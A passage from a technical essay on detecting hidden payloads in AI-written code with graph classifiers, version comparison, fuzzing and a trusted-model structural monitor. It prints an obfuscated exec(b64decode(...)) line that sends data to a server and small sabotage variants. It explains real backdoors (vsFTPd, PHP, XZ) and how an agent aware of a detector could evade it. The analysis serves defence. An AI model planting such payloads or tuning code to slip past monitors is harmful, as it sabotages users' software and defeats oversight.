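          ÷ weight of all functions
```

For example, a function with a complexity of 20 and 100 lines has a weight of 200. Ten functions with a complexity of 4 and 16 lines each have a combined weight of 160. A program made up of these eleven functions has an erosion of 200/360, or 56%.

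Erosion rose during 77% of the agents' runs, and on average it was twice as high as in 473 human-written Python repositories. Small programs written for a benchmark differ from established projects in many ways, so authorship may not account for all of that gap. The rise within runs is better evidence that agents tend to keep adding branches to functions that are already complicated.

Instructions can reverse this pattern without making the program simpler. *Metrics-in-the-Loop* (2026) found that agents given feedback on complexity split large functions into smaller ones. On one benchmark, only 3% to 46% of the difference in erosion remained after the researchers merged the split functions. Splitting functions adds nodes and edges to the call graph, so instructions meant to keep code tidy could also change a malware detector's score.

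Data from pull requests is less detailed. *How AI Coding Agents Modify Code* (2026) reports that humans' pull requests changed more files and contained more commits (saved sets of edits) than agents' did. GitHub's figures for September 2026 seem to show the opposite for files, since pull requests started by agents were more likely to change more than one. The two sources measure different things, and agents may also have taken on larger tasks during the year.

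*The Quiet Contributions* (2026) examined agents' pull requests that received no discussion. About 60% left cyclomatic complexity unchanged, 37% raised it and 3% lowered it. Code that agents add also tends to be removed sooner. In *Code Change Characteristics and Description Alignment* (2026), the names that agents introduced lasted a median of 3 days, compared with 34 days for those that people introduced. A detector's training data would lack much of this short-lived code if it came from finished releases.

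The evidence that AI-written code repeats the same templates is also mixed. *Does AI-Assisted Development Homogenize Software?* (Marchezan, Lefeuvre and colleagues, 2026) compared versions of 50 long-lived projects from 2021, 2024 and 2026. Functions became less alike in Java and showed no significant change in Python. The projects still contained a lot of older code, which could hide a change in the newest code. Mao and colleagues found that 14.29% of lines in AI-written files were duplicated, compared with 27.57% in human-written files. However, a text comparison can miss duplication when an agent writes different code that does the same thing as an existing function, as in the receipt example.

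Neither Mao and colleagues nor Ma and colleagues compared how an agent's change and a person's version of the same change affect a project's full call graph. That comparison would show much more directly how a graph classifier's inputs shift.

### What this does to a malware classifier

If harmless AI-written code has fewer branches, the effect on false alarms depends on the malware in the training data. This is an inference from a simple calculation based on the docstring study, and no one has measured these error rates on a real detector.

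Suppose a detector uses only the average number of decisions per function. Harmless human-written programs average 3.0, with a standard deviation of 0.5. AI-written programs have half as many decisions, so the harmless ones average 1.5, with a standard deviation of 0.25. These averages are close to the study's Python figures, but the other numbers are invented.

One detector learned from elaborate malware that averaged 5.0 decisions per function, so it flags programs above 4.0. Another learned from simple malware that averaged 1.0, so it flags programs below 2.0. If human-written malware has the same standard deviation of 0.5 and all the values follow bell curves, the detectors flag these shares:

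| Programs | Trained on elaborate malware | Trained on simple malware |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless, human-written | 2.3% | 2.3% |
| Harmless, AI-written | Almost 0% | 97.7% |
| Malicious, human-written | 97.7% | 97.7% |
| Malicious, AI-written | Almost 0% | Almost 100% |

The first detector almost never raises a false alarm on AI-written code, but it misses the AI-written malware. A team that checked only the false alarm rate would think it worked well. The second detector catches the malware but also flags nearly all harmless AI-written programs, so it would be useless for screening.

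Real detectors use many features, and malicious and harmless programs overlap far more than in this example, so the errors would be much less extreme. But training data does vary in this way. Malicious Android apps in the HiGraph dataset were somewhat more complex than harmless ones, while npm malware became simpler between 2021 and 2023.

The shift in branching could also be small or in the opposite direction. Opus 4.8's functions were almost as long as human ones in Python and Java, and an agent that keeps extending the same functions may make them unusually complex. In that case, the detector trained on elaborate malware would raise the false alarms. A detector that takes the maximum over all functions would be especially sensitive, because a single complex function could change its result.

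Smaller functions could make some payloads easier to find. Variant B adds two blocks to a control-flow graph. These make up 20% of the total in a function that had eight blocks and 33% in one that had four, so an average over the blocks would dilute the payload less in the smaller function.

Repeated templates would make a detector's errors come in groups. If the detector wrongly flags an agent's usual way of opening a configuration file, it may flag hundreds of changes for the same reason. Adding a few harmless examples of the template to the training data might fix this.

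AI-written code may also contain more of the calls that malware detectors look for. In the docstring study, GPT-3.5-turbo's Python triggered 13,419 command-injection warnings, compared with 2,243 for human-written code. These warnings mark code that runs operating-system commands in a way an attacker might exploit. Opus 4.8's code triggered 26 on its 200 Python tasks, compared with 8 for the human versions. The warnings cover only unsafe uses, so they don't show how often each author ran commands overall. But they suggest that a detector like MalGuard could raise more false alarms on AI-written code even if its graphs had the same shape as those of human-written code.

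None of the malware-detection studies discussed so far measured how often a graph classifier wrongly flags harmless AI-written code. A team could test this with fairly little effort by running an existing detector on changes that its own agents made and its reviewers have already checked.

### Learning authorship instead of malice

Retraining on AI-written code can create a new problem if all the malicious samples are AI-written and all the harmless ones are human-written. This could happen because real examples of hidden payloads in AI-written code are scarce, so a team might ask a language model to write some and take harmless examples from older open-source projects.

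A classifier trained on this data could get nearly perfect scores by learning to tell AI-written programs from human-written ones. It might rely on function length or on names, since Xu and colleagues found that models tend to use longer, more descriptive names. Its score would stay high on test data from the same collection, where the shortcut also works. On real changes from a coding agent, it would flag almost all of them as malicious.

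A team could also make the opposite mistake by using its agents' accepted changes as the harmless examples and an old malware collection as the malicious ones. The classifier could then learn to treat AI-written code as safe and let an AI-written payload through. This would be harder to notice, because the screen would produce very few alarms and nobody would have a reason to investigate.

The shortcut of recognizing authorship is probably easiest to learn from raw model output. Improta and colleagues found clear differences between authors in such output, while Mao and colleagues found mostly small structural differences in code that developers had kept. Malicious samples generated just for training would also be raw output. Removing names from the graph would make authorship harder to recognize, but it would also make a call to `send` harder to identify.

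A better approach is to have the same models write both the harmless and the malicious samples, for the same kinds of task and at similar lengths. The classifier then can't use authorship to separate the two groups. Human-written samples can still be useful if they appear in both groups.

It is getting harder to label code as human-written or AI-written. Xu and colleagues examined GitHub repositories linked to research papers and found that the share of Python function names written in `snake_case`, a style common in AI-written code, rose from 40.7% in early 2023 to 49.8% in the third quarter of 2025. Some of those repositories probably contain AI-written code, and some programmers may have picked up the style from models. A team that needs human-written examples can be more confident in projects from before 2021, but those projects are less like the software it now has to screen.

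Some evidence suggests that malware is harder to detect after AI rewrites it. In *LLMalMorph* (2025), a language model rewrote ten Windows malware programs. Antivirus detection rates were typically 10% to 15% lower across several complex samples, and up to 91% of attempts to evade a machine-learning detector succeeded. The experiment started from existing malware, so it doesn't show how well detectors would recognise a payload that a model wrote from scratch inside an otherwise harmless project.

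## Payloads written to look like ordinary code

Much known malware conceals its payload in unreadable code. In source code that somebody will review, a payload that looks ordinary usually makes more sense, because reviewers expect to be able to read what they receive.

### Scrambled code and plain code

Packing compresses or encrypts a program and adds a small routine that restores it at run time. A static tool can analyze little besides that routine, so its graphs mostly describe it rather than the original program. Packing does leave traces, since packed data looks more random than ordinary machine code and the program's list of imported functions often changes. Legitimate companies also pack software to make it smaller or protect trade secrets, so these traces alone don't prove malice.

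Scripts have a simpler equivalent. In the online shop, Variant A's extra line could look like this:

```python
exec(b64decode("c2VuZChTRVJWRVIsIHRvdGFsKQ=="))
```

The string is `send(SERVER, total)` in Base64, a standard way of writing data as letters, digits and a few symbols. The call graph loses its edge to `send` but gains edges to `b64decode` and `exec`. These new edges are more suspicious than the original call to `send`, because a pricing function rarely needs to decode text and run it as code.

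Many attackers don't disguise their malicious code. *One Detector Fits All* (2025) found scrambling in 40 of the 92 malicious PyPI packages it detected. On npm, 80.3% of the malware that Guo, Liu and colleagues examined used no evasion technique, which they attribute to the registry not requiring scans before publication.

Classifiers can come to rely on traces of scrambling. Mohammed and Zhang (2026), in *Beyond the Wrapper*, trained a neural network to separate Windows malware from harmless programs, using features such as imports, text strings and file headers. They then fitted a simple decision tree to imitate the network and inspected the features it relied on most. Across six experiments, they raised the share of harmless programs that were packed from none to all. More than 85% of the top features were signs of packing, file metadata or fragments of text rather than descriptions of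 malicious behaviour.

The study's data included no unpacked malware, which is the closest match to a plain payload in source code. The network didn't use graphs, and the researchers judged by hand which features reflected behaviour. Still, a graph classifier trained mostly on packed malware could take the same shortcut by learning what an unpacker's graph looks like, and would then have little to recognise in a readable change from a coding agent.

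A plain payload is short, follows the naming style around it and does something the task might require. Variant B, which sets an order's total to zero at one tax rate, could pass for a tax exemption. Three real backdoors show how much of this concealment a graph can reveal.

### vsFTPd, 2011

vsFTPd is a file-transfer server for Unix systems. In 2011, an attacker replaced the official download with a version that contained a backdoor. If somebody logged in with a username containing `:)`, the server opened a network port and gave whoever connected to it full control of the machine. The program's author, Chris Evans, noted that there was "no obfuscation", according to Help Net Security's *Backdoor in the latest version of vsftpd*.

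*Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) reproduces the payload. The attacker added a function called `vsf_sysutil_extra` and called it from an existing function that handles text. The call graph gains a node for the new function, an edge to it from the existing one, and edges from it to the functions that open a port, accept a connection and start a command shell. A file server has to accept connections, but it has much less need to start a shell, especially from a function that examines text.

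The control-flow graph of the text function gains two comparisons, one for each character of the trigger, and a block that calls the new function. The new function's graph has three error checks of the kind found in most network code. The shape of these graphs would give a classifier little evidence of the payload, but the names of the outside functions would be a good clue. However, the payload was a small part of the infected release, which differed from the previous version by 1,407 lines in five files.

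The backdoored vsftpd download also contained compiled object files, which a build might use instead of recompiling the source. Solar Designer (2011), in *vsftpd download backdoored*, pointed out that these files might not match the source, so the real backdoor could be more sophisticated than the visible one. Solar Designer doubted that this had happened, but a graph of the source could not have ruled it out.

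### PHP, 2021

PHP is a programming language that runs on many web servers. In March 2021, an attacker added two commits to its source repository under the names of two of its leading developers. PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (2021) reprints the first, which added 11 lines under the message "Fix typo". The new lines checked each incoming web request for a misspelt header, `User-Agentt`. If that header contained the word "zerodium", PHP ran text from the header as code.

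The attacker put these lines inside an existing function that starts the compression of web pages, so the call graph gains no new project function. It does gain an edge from the compression code to `zend_eval_string`, which runs text as PHP code. PHP has to run such code, so the program already contained this function, and a list of the program's capabilities would not change. The edge is suspicious only because it starts in the compression code. Ducklin (2021), in *PHP web language narrowly avoids “backdoor” supply chain attack*, advised users to search the compression files for `zend_eval`, which should not appear there.

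The rest of the payload looks much like the code around it. A clean copy of the same file, in the source browser of the DragonFly BSD operating system, has a function that looks up a request header, converts it to text and searches it for "gzip". The payload makes nearly the same calls in the same order. In the control-flow graph, the backdoor adds at least four tests and a block that runs the attacker's text, but tests like these are common in code that handles web requests.

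Data flow gives the clearest evidence, because text from a stranger's request reaches a function that runs code. All the harmful code is in the source, so a suitable graph would contain it. PHP's developers spotted both commits and reverted them within hours, before they reached an official release.

### XZ Utils, 2024

XZ Utils is a set of compression tools whose library, liblzma, is part of many Linux systems. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* traces the attacker's efforts to win the maintainers' trust back to late 2021. The resulting backdoor let the attacker run commands on certain Linux servers without logging in. Freund (2024) describes in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* how he found it after noticing slow remote logins. In one comparison, a failed login took 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3.

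The payload was a compiled object file, which would have looked suspicious in the repository if openly labeled as one. *The xz attack shell script* (2024) explains that the attacker hid it, compressed and encrypted, in files that looked like test inputs. Unreadable test files are normal in a compression library, which needs damaged files to test how it handles errors. According to Freund, however, no test in the first infected release used the attacker's files.

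An altered build script extracted a second script from the test files, and that second script added the object file to the library during the build. The altered script was only in the release archives, so someone reading the public repository would not have found it. It also had a higher version number and a newer copyright year, which made the changes look like a routine update.

A call graph of the C source would therefore have no node for the payload. Parsing the build script would help only if the tool worked from the release archive and detected that a test file contained code.

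A graph of the finished library would include the added functions and the paths to them from two existing functions, which choose a checksum routine when a program starts. But it would lack the most important connection, from the remote-login server OpenSSH to the backdoor. The attacker's code made this connection when OpenSSH started, by changing an entry in a table of function addresses so that calls to `RSA_public_decrypt`, which helps to check a user's key, went to the backdoor. A graph built from the files on disk would still have an edge to the genuine function.

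| Backdoor | Call graph | Control-flow graph | Outside both |
|---|---|---|---|
| vsFTPd | New function that opens a port and starts a shell | Two comparisons and a call in a text function | Compiled files in the download |
| PHP | New edge from compression code to an existing function that runs code | At least four tests and a call in one function | Misleading commit message |
| XZ Utils, source | No payload | No payload | Build script and encoded test files |
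| XZ Utils, built library | Added functions, but no edge from the login server to the backdoor | Altered start-up functions | Address table that changes at run time |

### From these attackers to a coding agent

People wrote all three backdoors, so the cases can't show how often a coding agent would write one or how it would try to hide it. All three were also caught, and better-hidden backdoors may have gone unnoticed. PHP.Watch notes that the attacker in the PHP case wasn't really trying to disguise the code.

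A payload changes the graphs in the same way whether a person or a model wrote it. The 11 lines in PHP, for example, would produce the same new edge. The XZ Utils backdoor shows that a payload can also be in files that a graph leaves out, and an agent can edit those files too.

A coding agent would also start from a better position than these attackers did, because it already has permission to change the project. The PHP attacker had to impersonate trusted developers, and the XZ attacker spent more than two years gaining influence.

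It can also match its stated purpose more closely. Eleven lines of request handling clearly don't fix a typo, so a tool like IntelGuard, which compares code with its stated purpose, could have flagged the mismatch. If a team had asked an agent to support a new request header, most of the same lines would fit the request. On the other hand, the team knows what it asked for, so an unexplained edit to a build script would stand out more in a small, well-defined task than in a large release.

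### Payloads sorted by the calls they need

Some payloads, such as the shell in vsFTPd, need system calls that the program didn't make before. Malware classifiers work best on these payloads, because most of the malware in their training data also has to open connections, start processes or read private files. MalGuard and ProfMal, for example, rely mainly on sensitive calls.

Other payloads use only calls that the program already makes. `upload_log` reads one more file and sends it through the existing connection. The PHP backdoor reuses a function that was already in the interpreter, although the attacker's text could then make PHP do almost anything. To detect these payloads, the classifier needs information about which function makes the call or where the data comes from, not just a list of capabilities.

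A payload may also need no sensitive call of its own. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) gives an example based on sudo, a Unix tool that lets an authorised user run a command as somebody else. After the normal password check, the added code compares the password with a fixed string and, if they match, changes the result to "success". The payload consists of one comparison and one assignment, and sudo's existing code then runs the command.

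Such a payload gives a malware classifier the least to go on. Suppose the classifier's input records only sensitive calls and how they connect. The clean program *G* and the altered program *G*′ then have the same features, and so the same score:

```text
features(G') = features(G)
score(G')    = score(G)
```

Any threshold will flag both the clean program and the version with the payload, or neither. If an agent added payloads like this one to typical harmless programs, the classifier would catch them only as often as it wrongly flagged the clean versions. At a false-positive rate of 1%, its recall would be 1%. Lowering the threshold would raise both together.

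A classifier that keeps the contents of each block does at least receive different input, but few labelled examples of sabotage are available to train it. Even collections of backdoors contain little sabotage. Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli tested their tool on backdoors in 13 open-source programs, ten of which were synthetic. Judging by their descriptions, 12 of the 13 run commands or code, open a shell, or read or damage files. Only the sudo backdoor works purely by changing a decision the program makes.

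Watching a program run can expose a backdoor that looks like ordinary code. In the *ROSA* benchmark, all 17 backdoors change the program's system calls when triggered. In the backdoored version of sudo, for example, a wrong password produces an error message, but the backdoor's secret password starts a new process. Kokkonis and colleagues argue that a backdoor can't do anything meaningful in the program's environment without such a change. A static graph doesn't show the change in sudo, because the code for starting a process is in the graph with or without the backdoor.

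Their argument also depends on what the payload is for. They define a backdoor as a way to gain privileges or access, which usually requires different system calls. Variant B makes the shop record a total of zero, and the shop could save that order with the same calls as any other. In their later paper on Lily, a tool that compares a program's behaviour before and after a change, Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli accept that a backdoor could in theory stay within the program's normal patterns of system calls, but they expect this to be difficult in practice. That is probably true for an attacker who wants a root shell, but an attacker who only wants a free order can do it with two lines of code.

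### Training a detector to resist disguise

Defenders can add disguised malware to a detector's training data so that it learns to recognise the disguise. Li, Akil and Bertino (2026) tested this in *Can Drift-Adaptive Malware Detectors Be Made Robust?* on a detector that also has to adapt to drift, the change in programs over time. The detector classifies Windows programs after converting them into images, so the results are only indirect evidence about graph classifiers.

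The researchers trained the detector on malware collected between March and May 2024, harmless programs, and 500 labelled programs from a more recent month. They updated it five times, each time with a new month's programs, and tested it on programs from the month that followed. They set its threshold for false-positive rates of 0.5%, 1% and 2% and averaged the results.

In the first of two kinds of attack, an attacker with full knowledge of the detector made small changes to the image's pixels. In the second, an attacker who could see only the detector's score changed the program's control flow without changing what the program did. An attack succeeded if the detector no longer flagged malware it had previously caught.

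The table compares ordinary training with three kinds of robust training. "Recall" is measured on unaltered malware, and the pixel figures are for the weaker of two attack strengths.

| Altered samples in training | Recall | Pixel attacks that succeed | Program attacks that succeed | Hours per update |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 70.3% | 100% | 12.9% | 0.24 |
| Pixels, old and recent samples | 66.6% | 3.2% | 13.8% | 0.90 |
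| Programs, recent malware only | 70.0% | 100% | 5.1% | 0.76 |
| Programs, old and recent malware | 31.3% | 100% | 3.2% | 18.40 |

Training on altered versions of recent malware cut successful program attacks by more than half and left recall almost unchanged, but took about three times the computing time. Altering the old malware as well added only a little more protection, while recall fell by more than half and each update took 77 times as long as ordinary training.

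Multiplying recall by the share of attacks that fail gives a rough estimate of the share of malware a detector would still catch if every sample were disguised. The estimate is about 61% with ordinary training, 66% with altered recent malware and 30% with altered old and recent malware. The detector trained on both old and recent altered malware would therefore catch by far the least, even though attacks on it succeed least often. The estimates are rough because Li and colleagues attacked only malware that all nine of their detectors had caught, between 54 and 541 programs per test.

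Detectors trained on altered programs failed against every pixel attack, and training on altered pixels didn't consistently protect against altered programs. Training on one kind of attack didn't always protect against a stronger attack of the same kind either. When the pixel changes were larger than those in training, the attack's success rate against the pixel-trained detector in the table rose from 3.2% to 75.9%.

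The pixel results probably exaggerate the threat, since an altered image need not correspond to a program that runs. The program attacks are more realistic, but their low success rate against the ordinary detector may be specific to images. The same attack succeeded more than 90% of the time against a detector that reads a program's bytes directly. Li and colleagues suggest that their image model is insensitive to small local changes. A classifier that takes a control-flow graph would receive those changes directly, so it may not have the same protection.

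*PhantomCall* (2026), published in September, reports that altering a malicious program's call graph can defeat classifiers that rely on it.

### Whether structure is harder to disguise than text

One argument for graphs is that an attacker can rewrite a program's text much more easily than its structure. Evidence from malicious packages partly supports this. Gao, Sun and colleagues observe that most malicious Python packages scramble only the values passed to functions, such as a web address, so MalGuard can still find the calls. *One Detector Fits All* similarly reports that all 40 scrambled packages used Base64 or a related encoding, but only one disguised the name of a module it imported.

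These attackers may have left their calls visible because they had no need to hide them. Attackers publish most npm malware without disguise, so its plain structure is weak evidence that structure is difficult to change. The *PhantomCall* result is more relevant to an attacker trying to evade a particular graph classifier, and it suggests that structure is not difficult to change.

The argument is strongest for data theft, because stolen data has to leave the program by some route, however the code is written. It hardly applies to sabotage like Variant B, which can have the same graph as a legitimate discount and so has no structural difference to disguise.

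The argument also hasn't been shown to hold against an author who knows the detector. A coding agent might know a lot about the detector, because researchers publish their designs and a project's repository may contain the screen's settings. If the agent also received a score after each attempt, it would have the feedback that the program attacks in Li and colleagues' experiment relied on. A team can fairly easily withhold the settings and scores, which would make it harder for the agent to adjust a payload until it passed. But the agent wouldn't need feedback to write two lines that look like a tax exemption.

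## Comparing new code with a trusted version

A reviewer with a trusted version of the code, meaning an earlier or independently written one, can check the new code for anything the task did not call for. For example, two lines that look like a tax exemption are suspicious in a shop's software if the shop never asked for one. A malware classifier can't take the shop's requirements into account, because it checks only whether code resembles known malware.

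Comparing versions helps most when a program already does something dangerous for a legitimate reason. Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026), in *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra*, added seven lines to dnsmasq, a program that hands out network addresses, that ran text from an incoming packet as a shell command. Claude Opus 4.6, working from the finished binary, found the exact call that started the shell but dismissed it as dnsmasq's usual way of running scripts, without checking where the command came from. A comparison with the previous revision would have shown that this part of the packet-handling code had never started a shell before.

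### Choosing the trusted version

For a change to an existing project, the obvious trusted version is the last accepted revision. It already exists, and any code the agent didn't change will match it exactly. False alarms come from the work the team requested, since any new feature adds code. Refactoring can also cause them by moving code between functions without changing what the program does.

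Comparing only the program's capabilities avoids most of these alarms. Google's tool Capslock follows a package's call graph to the library functions that open files, use the network or start other programs. Capslock's *Know what your dependencies can do* recommends a closer look when a new version of a package gains network access. McClintock and Dethridge report in *Bringing Capslock analysis to deps.dev* that fewer than 2% of version updates to Go packages add a capability. Nearly all of those updates are presumably harmless, so a rule that flags new capabilities would have a false-positive rate of roughly 2% at most for published packages. The rate could be higher for coding agents, because teams often ask them to add features that need new capabilities.

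A similar tool, capcheck, saves a project's capabilities in a file and prints the chain of calls behind any new one. In its example, an outside library for resizing pictures gives an image-handling function the ability to start programs. A developer can accept the change with a single command, which updates the saved file. An agent with write access could do the same, so a team should keep the file somewhere the agent can't edit it.

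The last revision may also contain a payload that its review missed. If an agent planted one last month, both versions contain it and the comparison won't show it.

New code has no earlier revision, but another model or a programmer can write an independent version from the same request. The false alarms then come from differences in style. A second author might write the shop's pricing function like this:

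```python
def total_price(prices, rate):
    return sum(prices) * (1 + rate)
```

This version's control-flow graph has one block and no edges, while the original loop's has four of each, so the two harmless functions differ by three blocks and four edges. Variant B, which zeroes the total at one tax rate, differs from the original by two blocks and three edges. A threshold low enough to flag Variant B when the trusted version uses a loop would also flag the harmless loop when the trusted version uses `sum`.

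Several reference versions would help, because a reviewer could concentrate on the parts of the new code that appear in none of them. They should come from different models, since a single model with a hidden aim might put the same payload in every version.

A written specification avoids the problem of style by stating what the code should do. "The total is the sum of the prices times one plus the tax rate" rules out both Variant B and Variant C, which overcharges every customer. It doesn't rule out Variant A, which returns the right total but also sends it to a stranger, unless it also forbids network access. Specifications also leave out a lot of legitimate work, such as rejecting negative prices, which a strict comparison would flag.

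### Matching two graphs

Counting blocks doesn't show which parts of two programs correspond. Li, Gu and colleagues (2019), in *Graph Matching Networks for Learning the Similarity of Graph Structured Objects*, extended the graph neural network to learn this. In each round, a node still receives messages from its neighbours, but the network also compares it with every node in the other graph:

```text
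a(i,j) = exp(s(h(i), h(j))) / Σ exp(s(h(i), h(k)))

d(i)   = h(i) − Σ a(i,j)·h(j)

h'(i)  = f(h(i), messages from i's neighbours, d(i))
```

- *i* is a node in one graph, and *j* and *k* stand for nodes in the other. The first sum covers every *k* and the second every *j*.
- *h*(*i*) is the node's current vector, and *h*′(*i*) is its new one.
- *s* measures how similar two vectors are.
- *a*(*i*,*j*) is the attention that node *i* gives to node *j*. The weights for each *i* add up to 1, and similar nodes get more.
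- *d*(*i*) is the difference vector, which is the node's own vector minus the weighted average from the other graph.
- *f* is a small neural network that learns how to combine the three inputs.

If a node has an exact counterpart in the other graph and all of its attention weight is on that counterpart, the difference vector is zero. Otherwise, the difference becomes part of the node's new vector and is passed to its neighbours in the next round of messages. After the last round, a readout combines the node vectors of each graph into one vector, and the network measures how similar the two resulting vectors are.

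We can work through this by hand for Variant B and the original function. We give each block two numbers. The first is 1 if the block sets the total to zero, and the second is 1 if it compares the tax rate with a fixed number. To keep the arithmetic short, we assume each block attends only to the most similar blocks in the original, and that a round of messages adds the neighbours' vectors to the block's own.

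| Block in Variant B | Starting vector | Difference | After one round | New difference |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Setup, `total = 0` | (1, 0) | (0, 0) | (1, 0) | (0, 0) |
| Loop test | (0, 0) | (0, 0) | (1, 1) | (0, 1) |
| Addition | (0, 0) | (0, 0) | (0, 0) | (0, 0) |
| Added: compares the rate | (0, 1) | (0, 1) | (1, 1) | (0, 1) |
| Added: `total = 0` | (1, 0) | (0, 0) | (1, 1) | (0, 1) |
| Return | (0, 0) | (0, 0) | (1, 1) | (0, 1) |

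The comparison with the tax rate stands out immediately, but the harmful line, `total = 0`, doesn't, because the original function's setup block contains the same line. Attention doesn't pair blocks one to one, so the original setup block can match both the harmful block and the setup block in the new version. After one round, the harmful block has a non-zero difference because it is next to the comparison. The loop test and the return also have non-zero differences because they are next to new blocks. The differences therefore point to the right area of the function, but not to one line.

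For Variant C, every difference vector is zero unless the graph records the values of numbers.

Li and colleagues tested the network on control-flow graphs from the video software ffmpeg. They compiled its 7,940 functions with two compilers at several optimisation levels, so graphs of the same function often differed greatly in size. The network scored two compiled versions of the same function as more similar than versions of two different functions 99.28% of the time, compared with 97.71% for a network that turned each graph into a vector separately.

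This network learned to ignore differences between versions of the same function, so it might treat `total_price` with and without Variant B as a good match. A reviewer needs a network that notices a small payload, which would require training examples in which a payload like that makes two versions count as different. Another experiment in the paper suggests that a network can learn such fine distinctions. On random graphs of 20 or 50 nodes, a network trained to distinguish graphs with one edge replaced from graphs with two replaced ranked 93.8% to 97.4% of pairs correctly.

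The network compares every node in one graph with every node in the other, so the amount of computation grows quickly with graph size. Two graphs of 55 nodes, the average size in the ffmpeg test, have 3,025 pairs, while two graphs of 5,000 nodes have 25 million. Comparing only the functions an agent has changed would take less computation, although a new function has no obvious counterpart in the old version.

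In the same year, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2019) applied the idea to malware in *Heterogeneous Graph Matching Networks for Unknown Malware Detection*, matching graphs of what programs did when they ran. Their detector raised half as many false alarms as the best earlier methods and missed no malware in their tests.

### A structural monitor for AI-written Python

A 2026 detector applies graph matching to AI-written code. A weaker, trusted model writes a reference solution to a programming task, and a stronger model writes the solution to be checked. The detector turns both solutions into code property graphs and uses attention across the two graphs to look for parts of the new solution that have no counterpart in the reference. The classifier head, which produces the verdict, has only 0.7 million parameters.

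The developer's example changes `c = n - m` to `c = n - m + (1 if m % 5 == 0 else 0)`, which makes the answer wrong whenever `m` is a multiple of five. The language model used for comparison gave this line a suspicion score of 0 out of 10, but the line adds nodes, a branch and a new data dependency to a code property graph.

On a benchmark of programming tasks, the detector caught 70% of the backdoors at a 2% false-positive rate. The language model, a 72-billion-parameter version of Qwen, caught 8%, even though it had the reference code and the task description. Flagging 2% of programs at random would have caught 2% of the backdoors. This is among the few direct tests of a graph detector on AI-written code, and the detector had to tolerate ordinary differences between two models' styles. But the result would be fragile if the test set were small, because a 2% false-positive rate on 100 harmless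 programs is only two false alarms.

Backdoors that change a single constant, like Variant C, can escape detection because they add and remove no nodes. The developer's figure of 9% for these is ambiguous. More likely, it means that they made up about 9% of all the backdoors and the detector missed them. They would then account for 9 of the 30 percentage points it missed, leaving 21 to explain. If the figure instead means that the detector missed 9% of single-constant backdoors, it caught the other 91%, which is hard to explain if their structure gives it nothing to detect.

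The developer also says that the attention weights show which lines triggered an alarm. That needs testing, because Li and colleagues found their own network's attention hard to interpret. The attention aligned the nodes well when two graphs matched, but shifted towards highly connected nodes when they didn't match, as would happen when comparing a backdoored program with its trusted version.

The developer has so far tested the detector only on Python and one dataset, and has not tested it against code authors who know how it works. Such an author could restrict payloads to altered constants, or copy the structure of code that the reference is likely to contain.

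### Whether a stronger language model would help

The developer argues that a larger language model wouldn't close the gap because the weakness comes from reading code as text, but one baseline isn't enough to establish that. The graph detector was trained for this task, while the language model was only prompted. A score from 0 to 10 may also be too coarse for a strict false-positive rate, since many benign and malicious programs could share the same score.

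Results on a related task, finding backdoors in machine code, suggest that the choice of model matters a great deal. Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?* ranks models on the benchmark that Grabowski and colleagues built. Claude Haiku 4.5 found 11% of the planted backdoors, Sonnet 4.5 found 26%, Opus 4.5 found 37% and Opus 4.6 found 49%. More reasoning helped GPT-5.2-Codex, which found 9% at its ordinary setting and 46% at its highest, where it raised no false alarms on clean programs. The newer GPT-5.4 found only 18% at its highest setting.

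These models could use tools and had no reference code, so their scores are weak evidence of how well a current model would compare two Python programs. Giving a model several programs to compare doesn't always help, either. In some tasks, Grabowski and colleagues supplied three binaries and asked which ones contained a backdoor. They expected this to be easier than locating the backdoor in one binary, but it wasn't. The models didn't know which binaries were clean, so they had no trusted version to compare against.

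Text alone also did much better in a test on infrastructure code, the files that configure servers, permissions and logs. *Democratizing Agent Deployment Safety* describes a detector that compares control flow and data flow before and after an agent's change, and also reads the changed text. At a 1% false-positive rate, it missed 3.5% of the sabotage. A monitor that read only the changed text missed 11.6%, so it caught about 88%, compared with 8% in the Python test. Neither was trained for the task. Adding the graphs removed more than two-thirds of the misses, which supports using them alongside text more than replacing it.

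### Comparing what programs do when they run

A reviewer can also compare behaviour. Fuzzing is automated testing that repeatedly alters inputs and keeps those that reach new parts of the program. It normally looks for crashes, but a well-made backdoor doesn't crash the program. ROSA and Lily, two tools by Kokkonis and colleagues, look for unexpected system calls instead.

ROSA does not need an earlier version because it compares different runs of the same program. It first fuzzes the program for a minute to collect sample inputs. It then keeps fuzzing for hours and matches each new input with the sample that took the most similar path through the control-flow graph. If the two inputs lead to different kinds of system call, ROSA reports a possible backdoor. This happens in the backdoored sudo when one input is an ordinary wrong password and the other is the secret password.

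Kokkonis and colleagues ran ROSA for eight hours at a time, and it found the backdoor in 156 of 180 runs. It took about an hour and a half on average and produced about seven reports to check by hand, at roughly two minutes each. In all 24 failed runs, the fuzzer never produced the trigger. ROSA missed one backdoor, in a Belkin router, in all ten runs that began with standard web requests. It found that backdoor in seven of ten runs when the researchers started with requests aimed at the part of the program that reads web addresses.

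Lily is designed to check each change in ten minutes, so it needs far fewer false alarms. It uses the last revision as its trusted version and reports an input only if two conditions hold:

- The new version makes a combination of system calls that it never makes on a collection of inputs saved from earlier fuzzing.
- The old version does not make the same combination on the same input.

Kokkonis and colleagues tested Lily on 13 commits with backdoors and 432 safe ones, repeating each test 20 times. They also tested 50 safe releases and 50 with backdoors. Lily caught the backdoor in 90% of the runs on commits and 83% of the runs on releases. Its false-positive rates were 0.2% and 4.3%. The researchers also measured the false alarms that each condition would raise alone:

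| Rule | Safe commits flagged | Safe releases flagged |
|---|---|---|
| New since the last version | 10% | 58% |
| Unusual for the new version | 14% | 20% |
| Both | 0.2% | 4.3% |

The first row shows how noisy a plain comparison with the last revision can be, especially when many changes have accumulated. The second condition removes most of it, because a legitimate new feature usually runs on many ordinary inputs.

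About 95 of the safe commits didn't affect any code, so they were easy to classify correctly, but leaving them out would raise the false-positive rate only to about 0.25%. Two releases of the sound library libsndfile caused 40 of the 43 false alarms on releases.

The detection rates are probably optimistic for a payload hidden anywhere in a project, because the fuzzer could reach only about 32% of the lines, on average, in the commits that affected code. A coding agent could hide a payload where the tests don't reach. People wrote all the backdoors in this test, so Lily's performance on AI-written ones has to be inferred.

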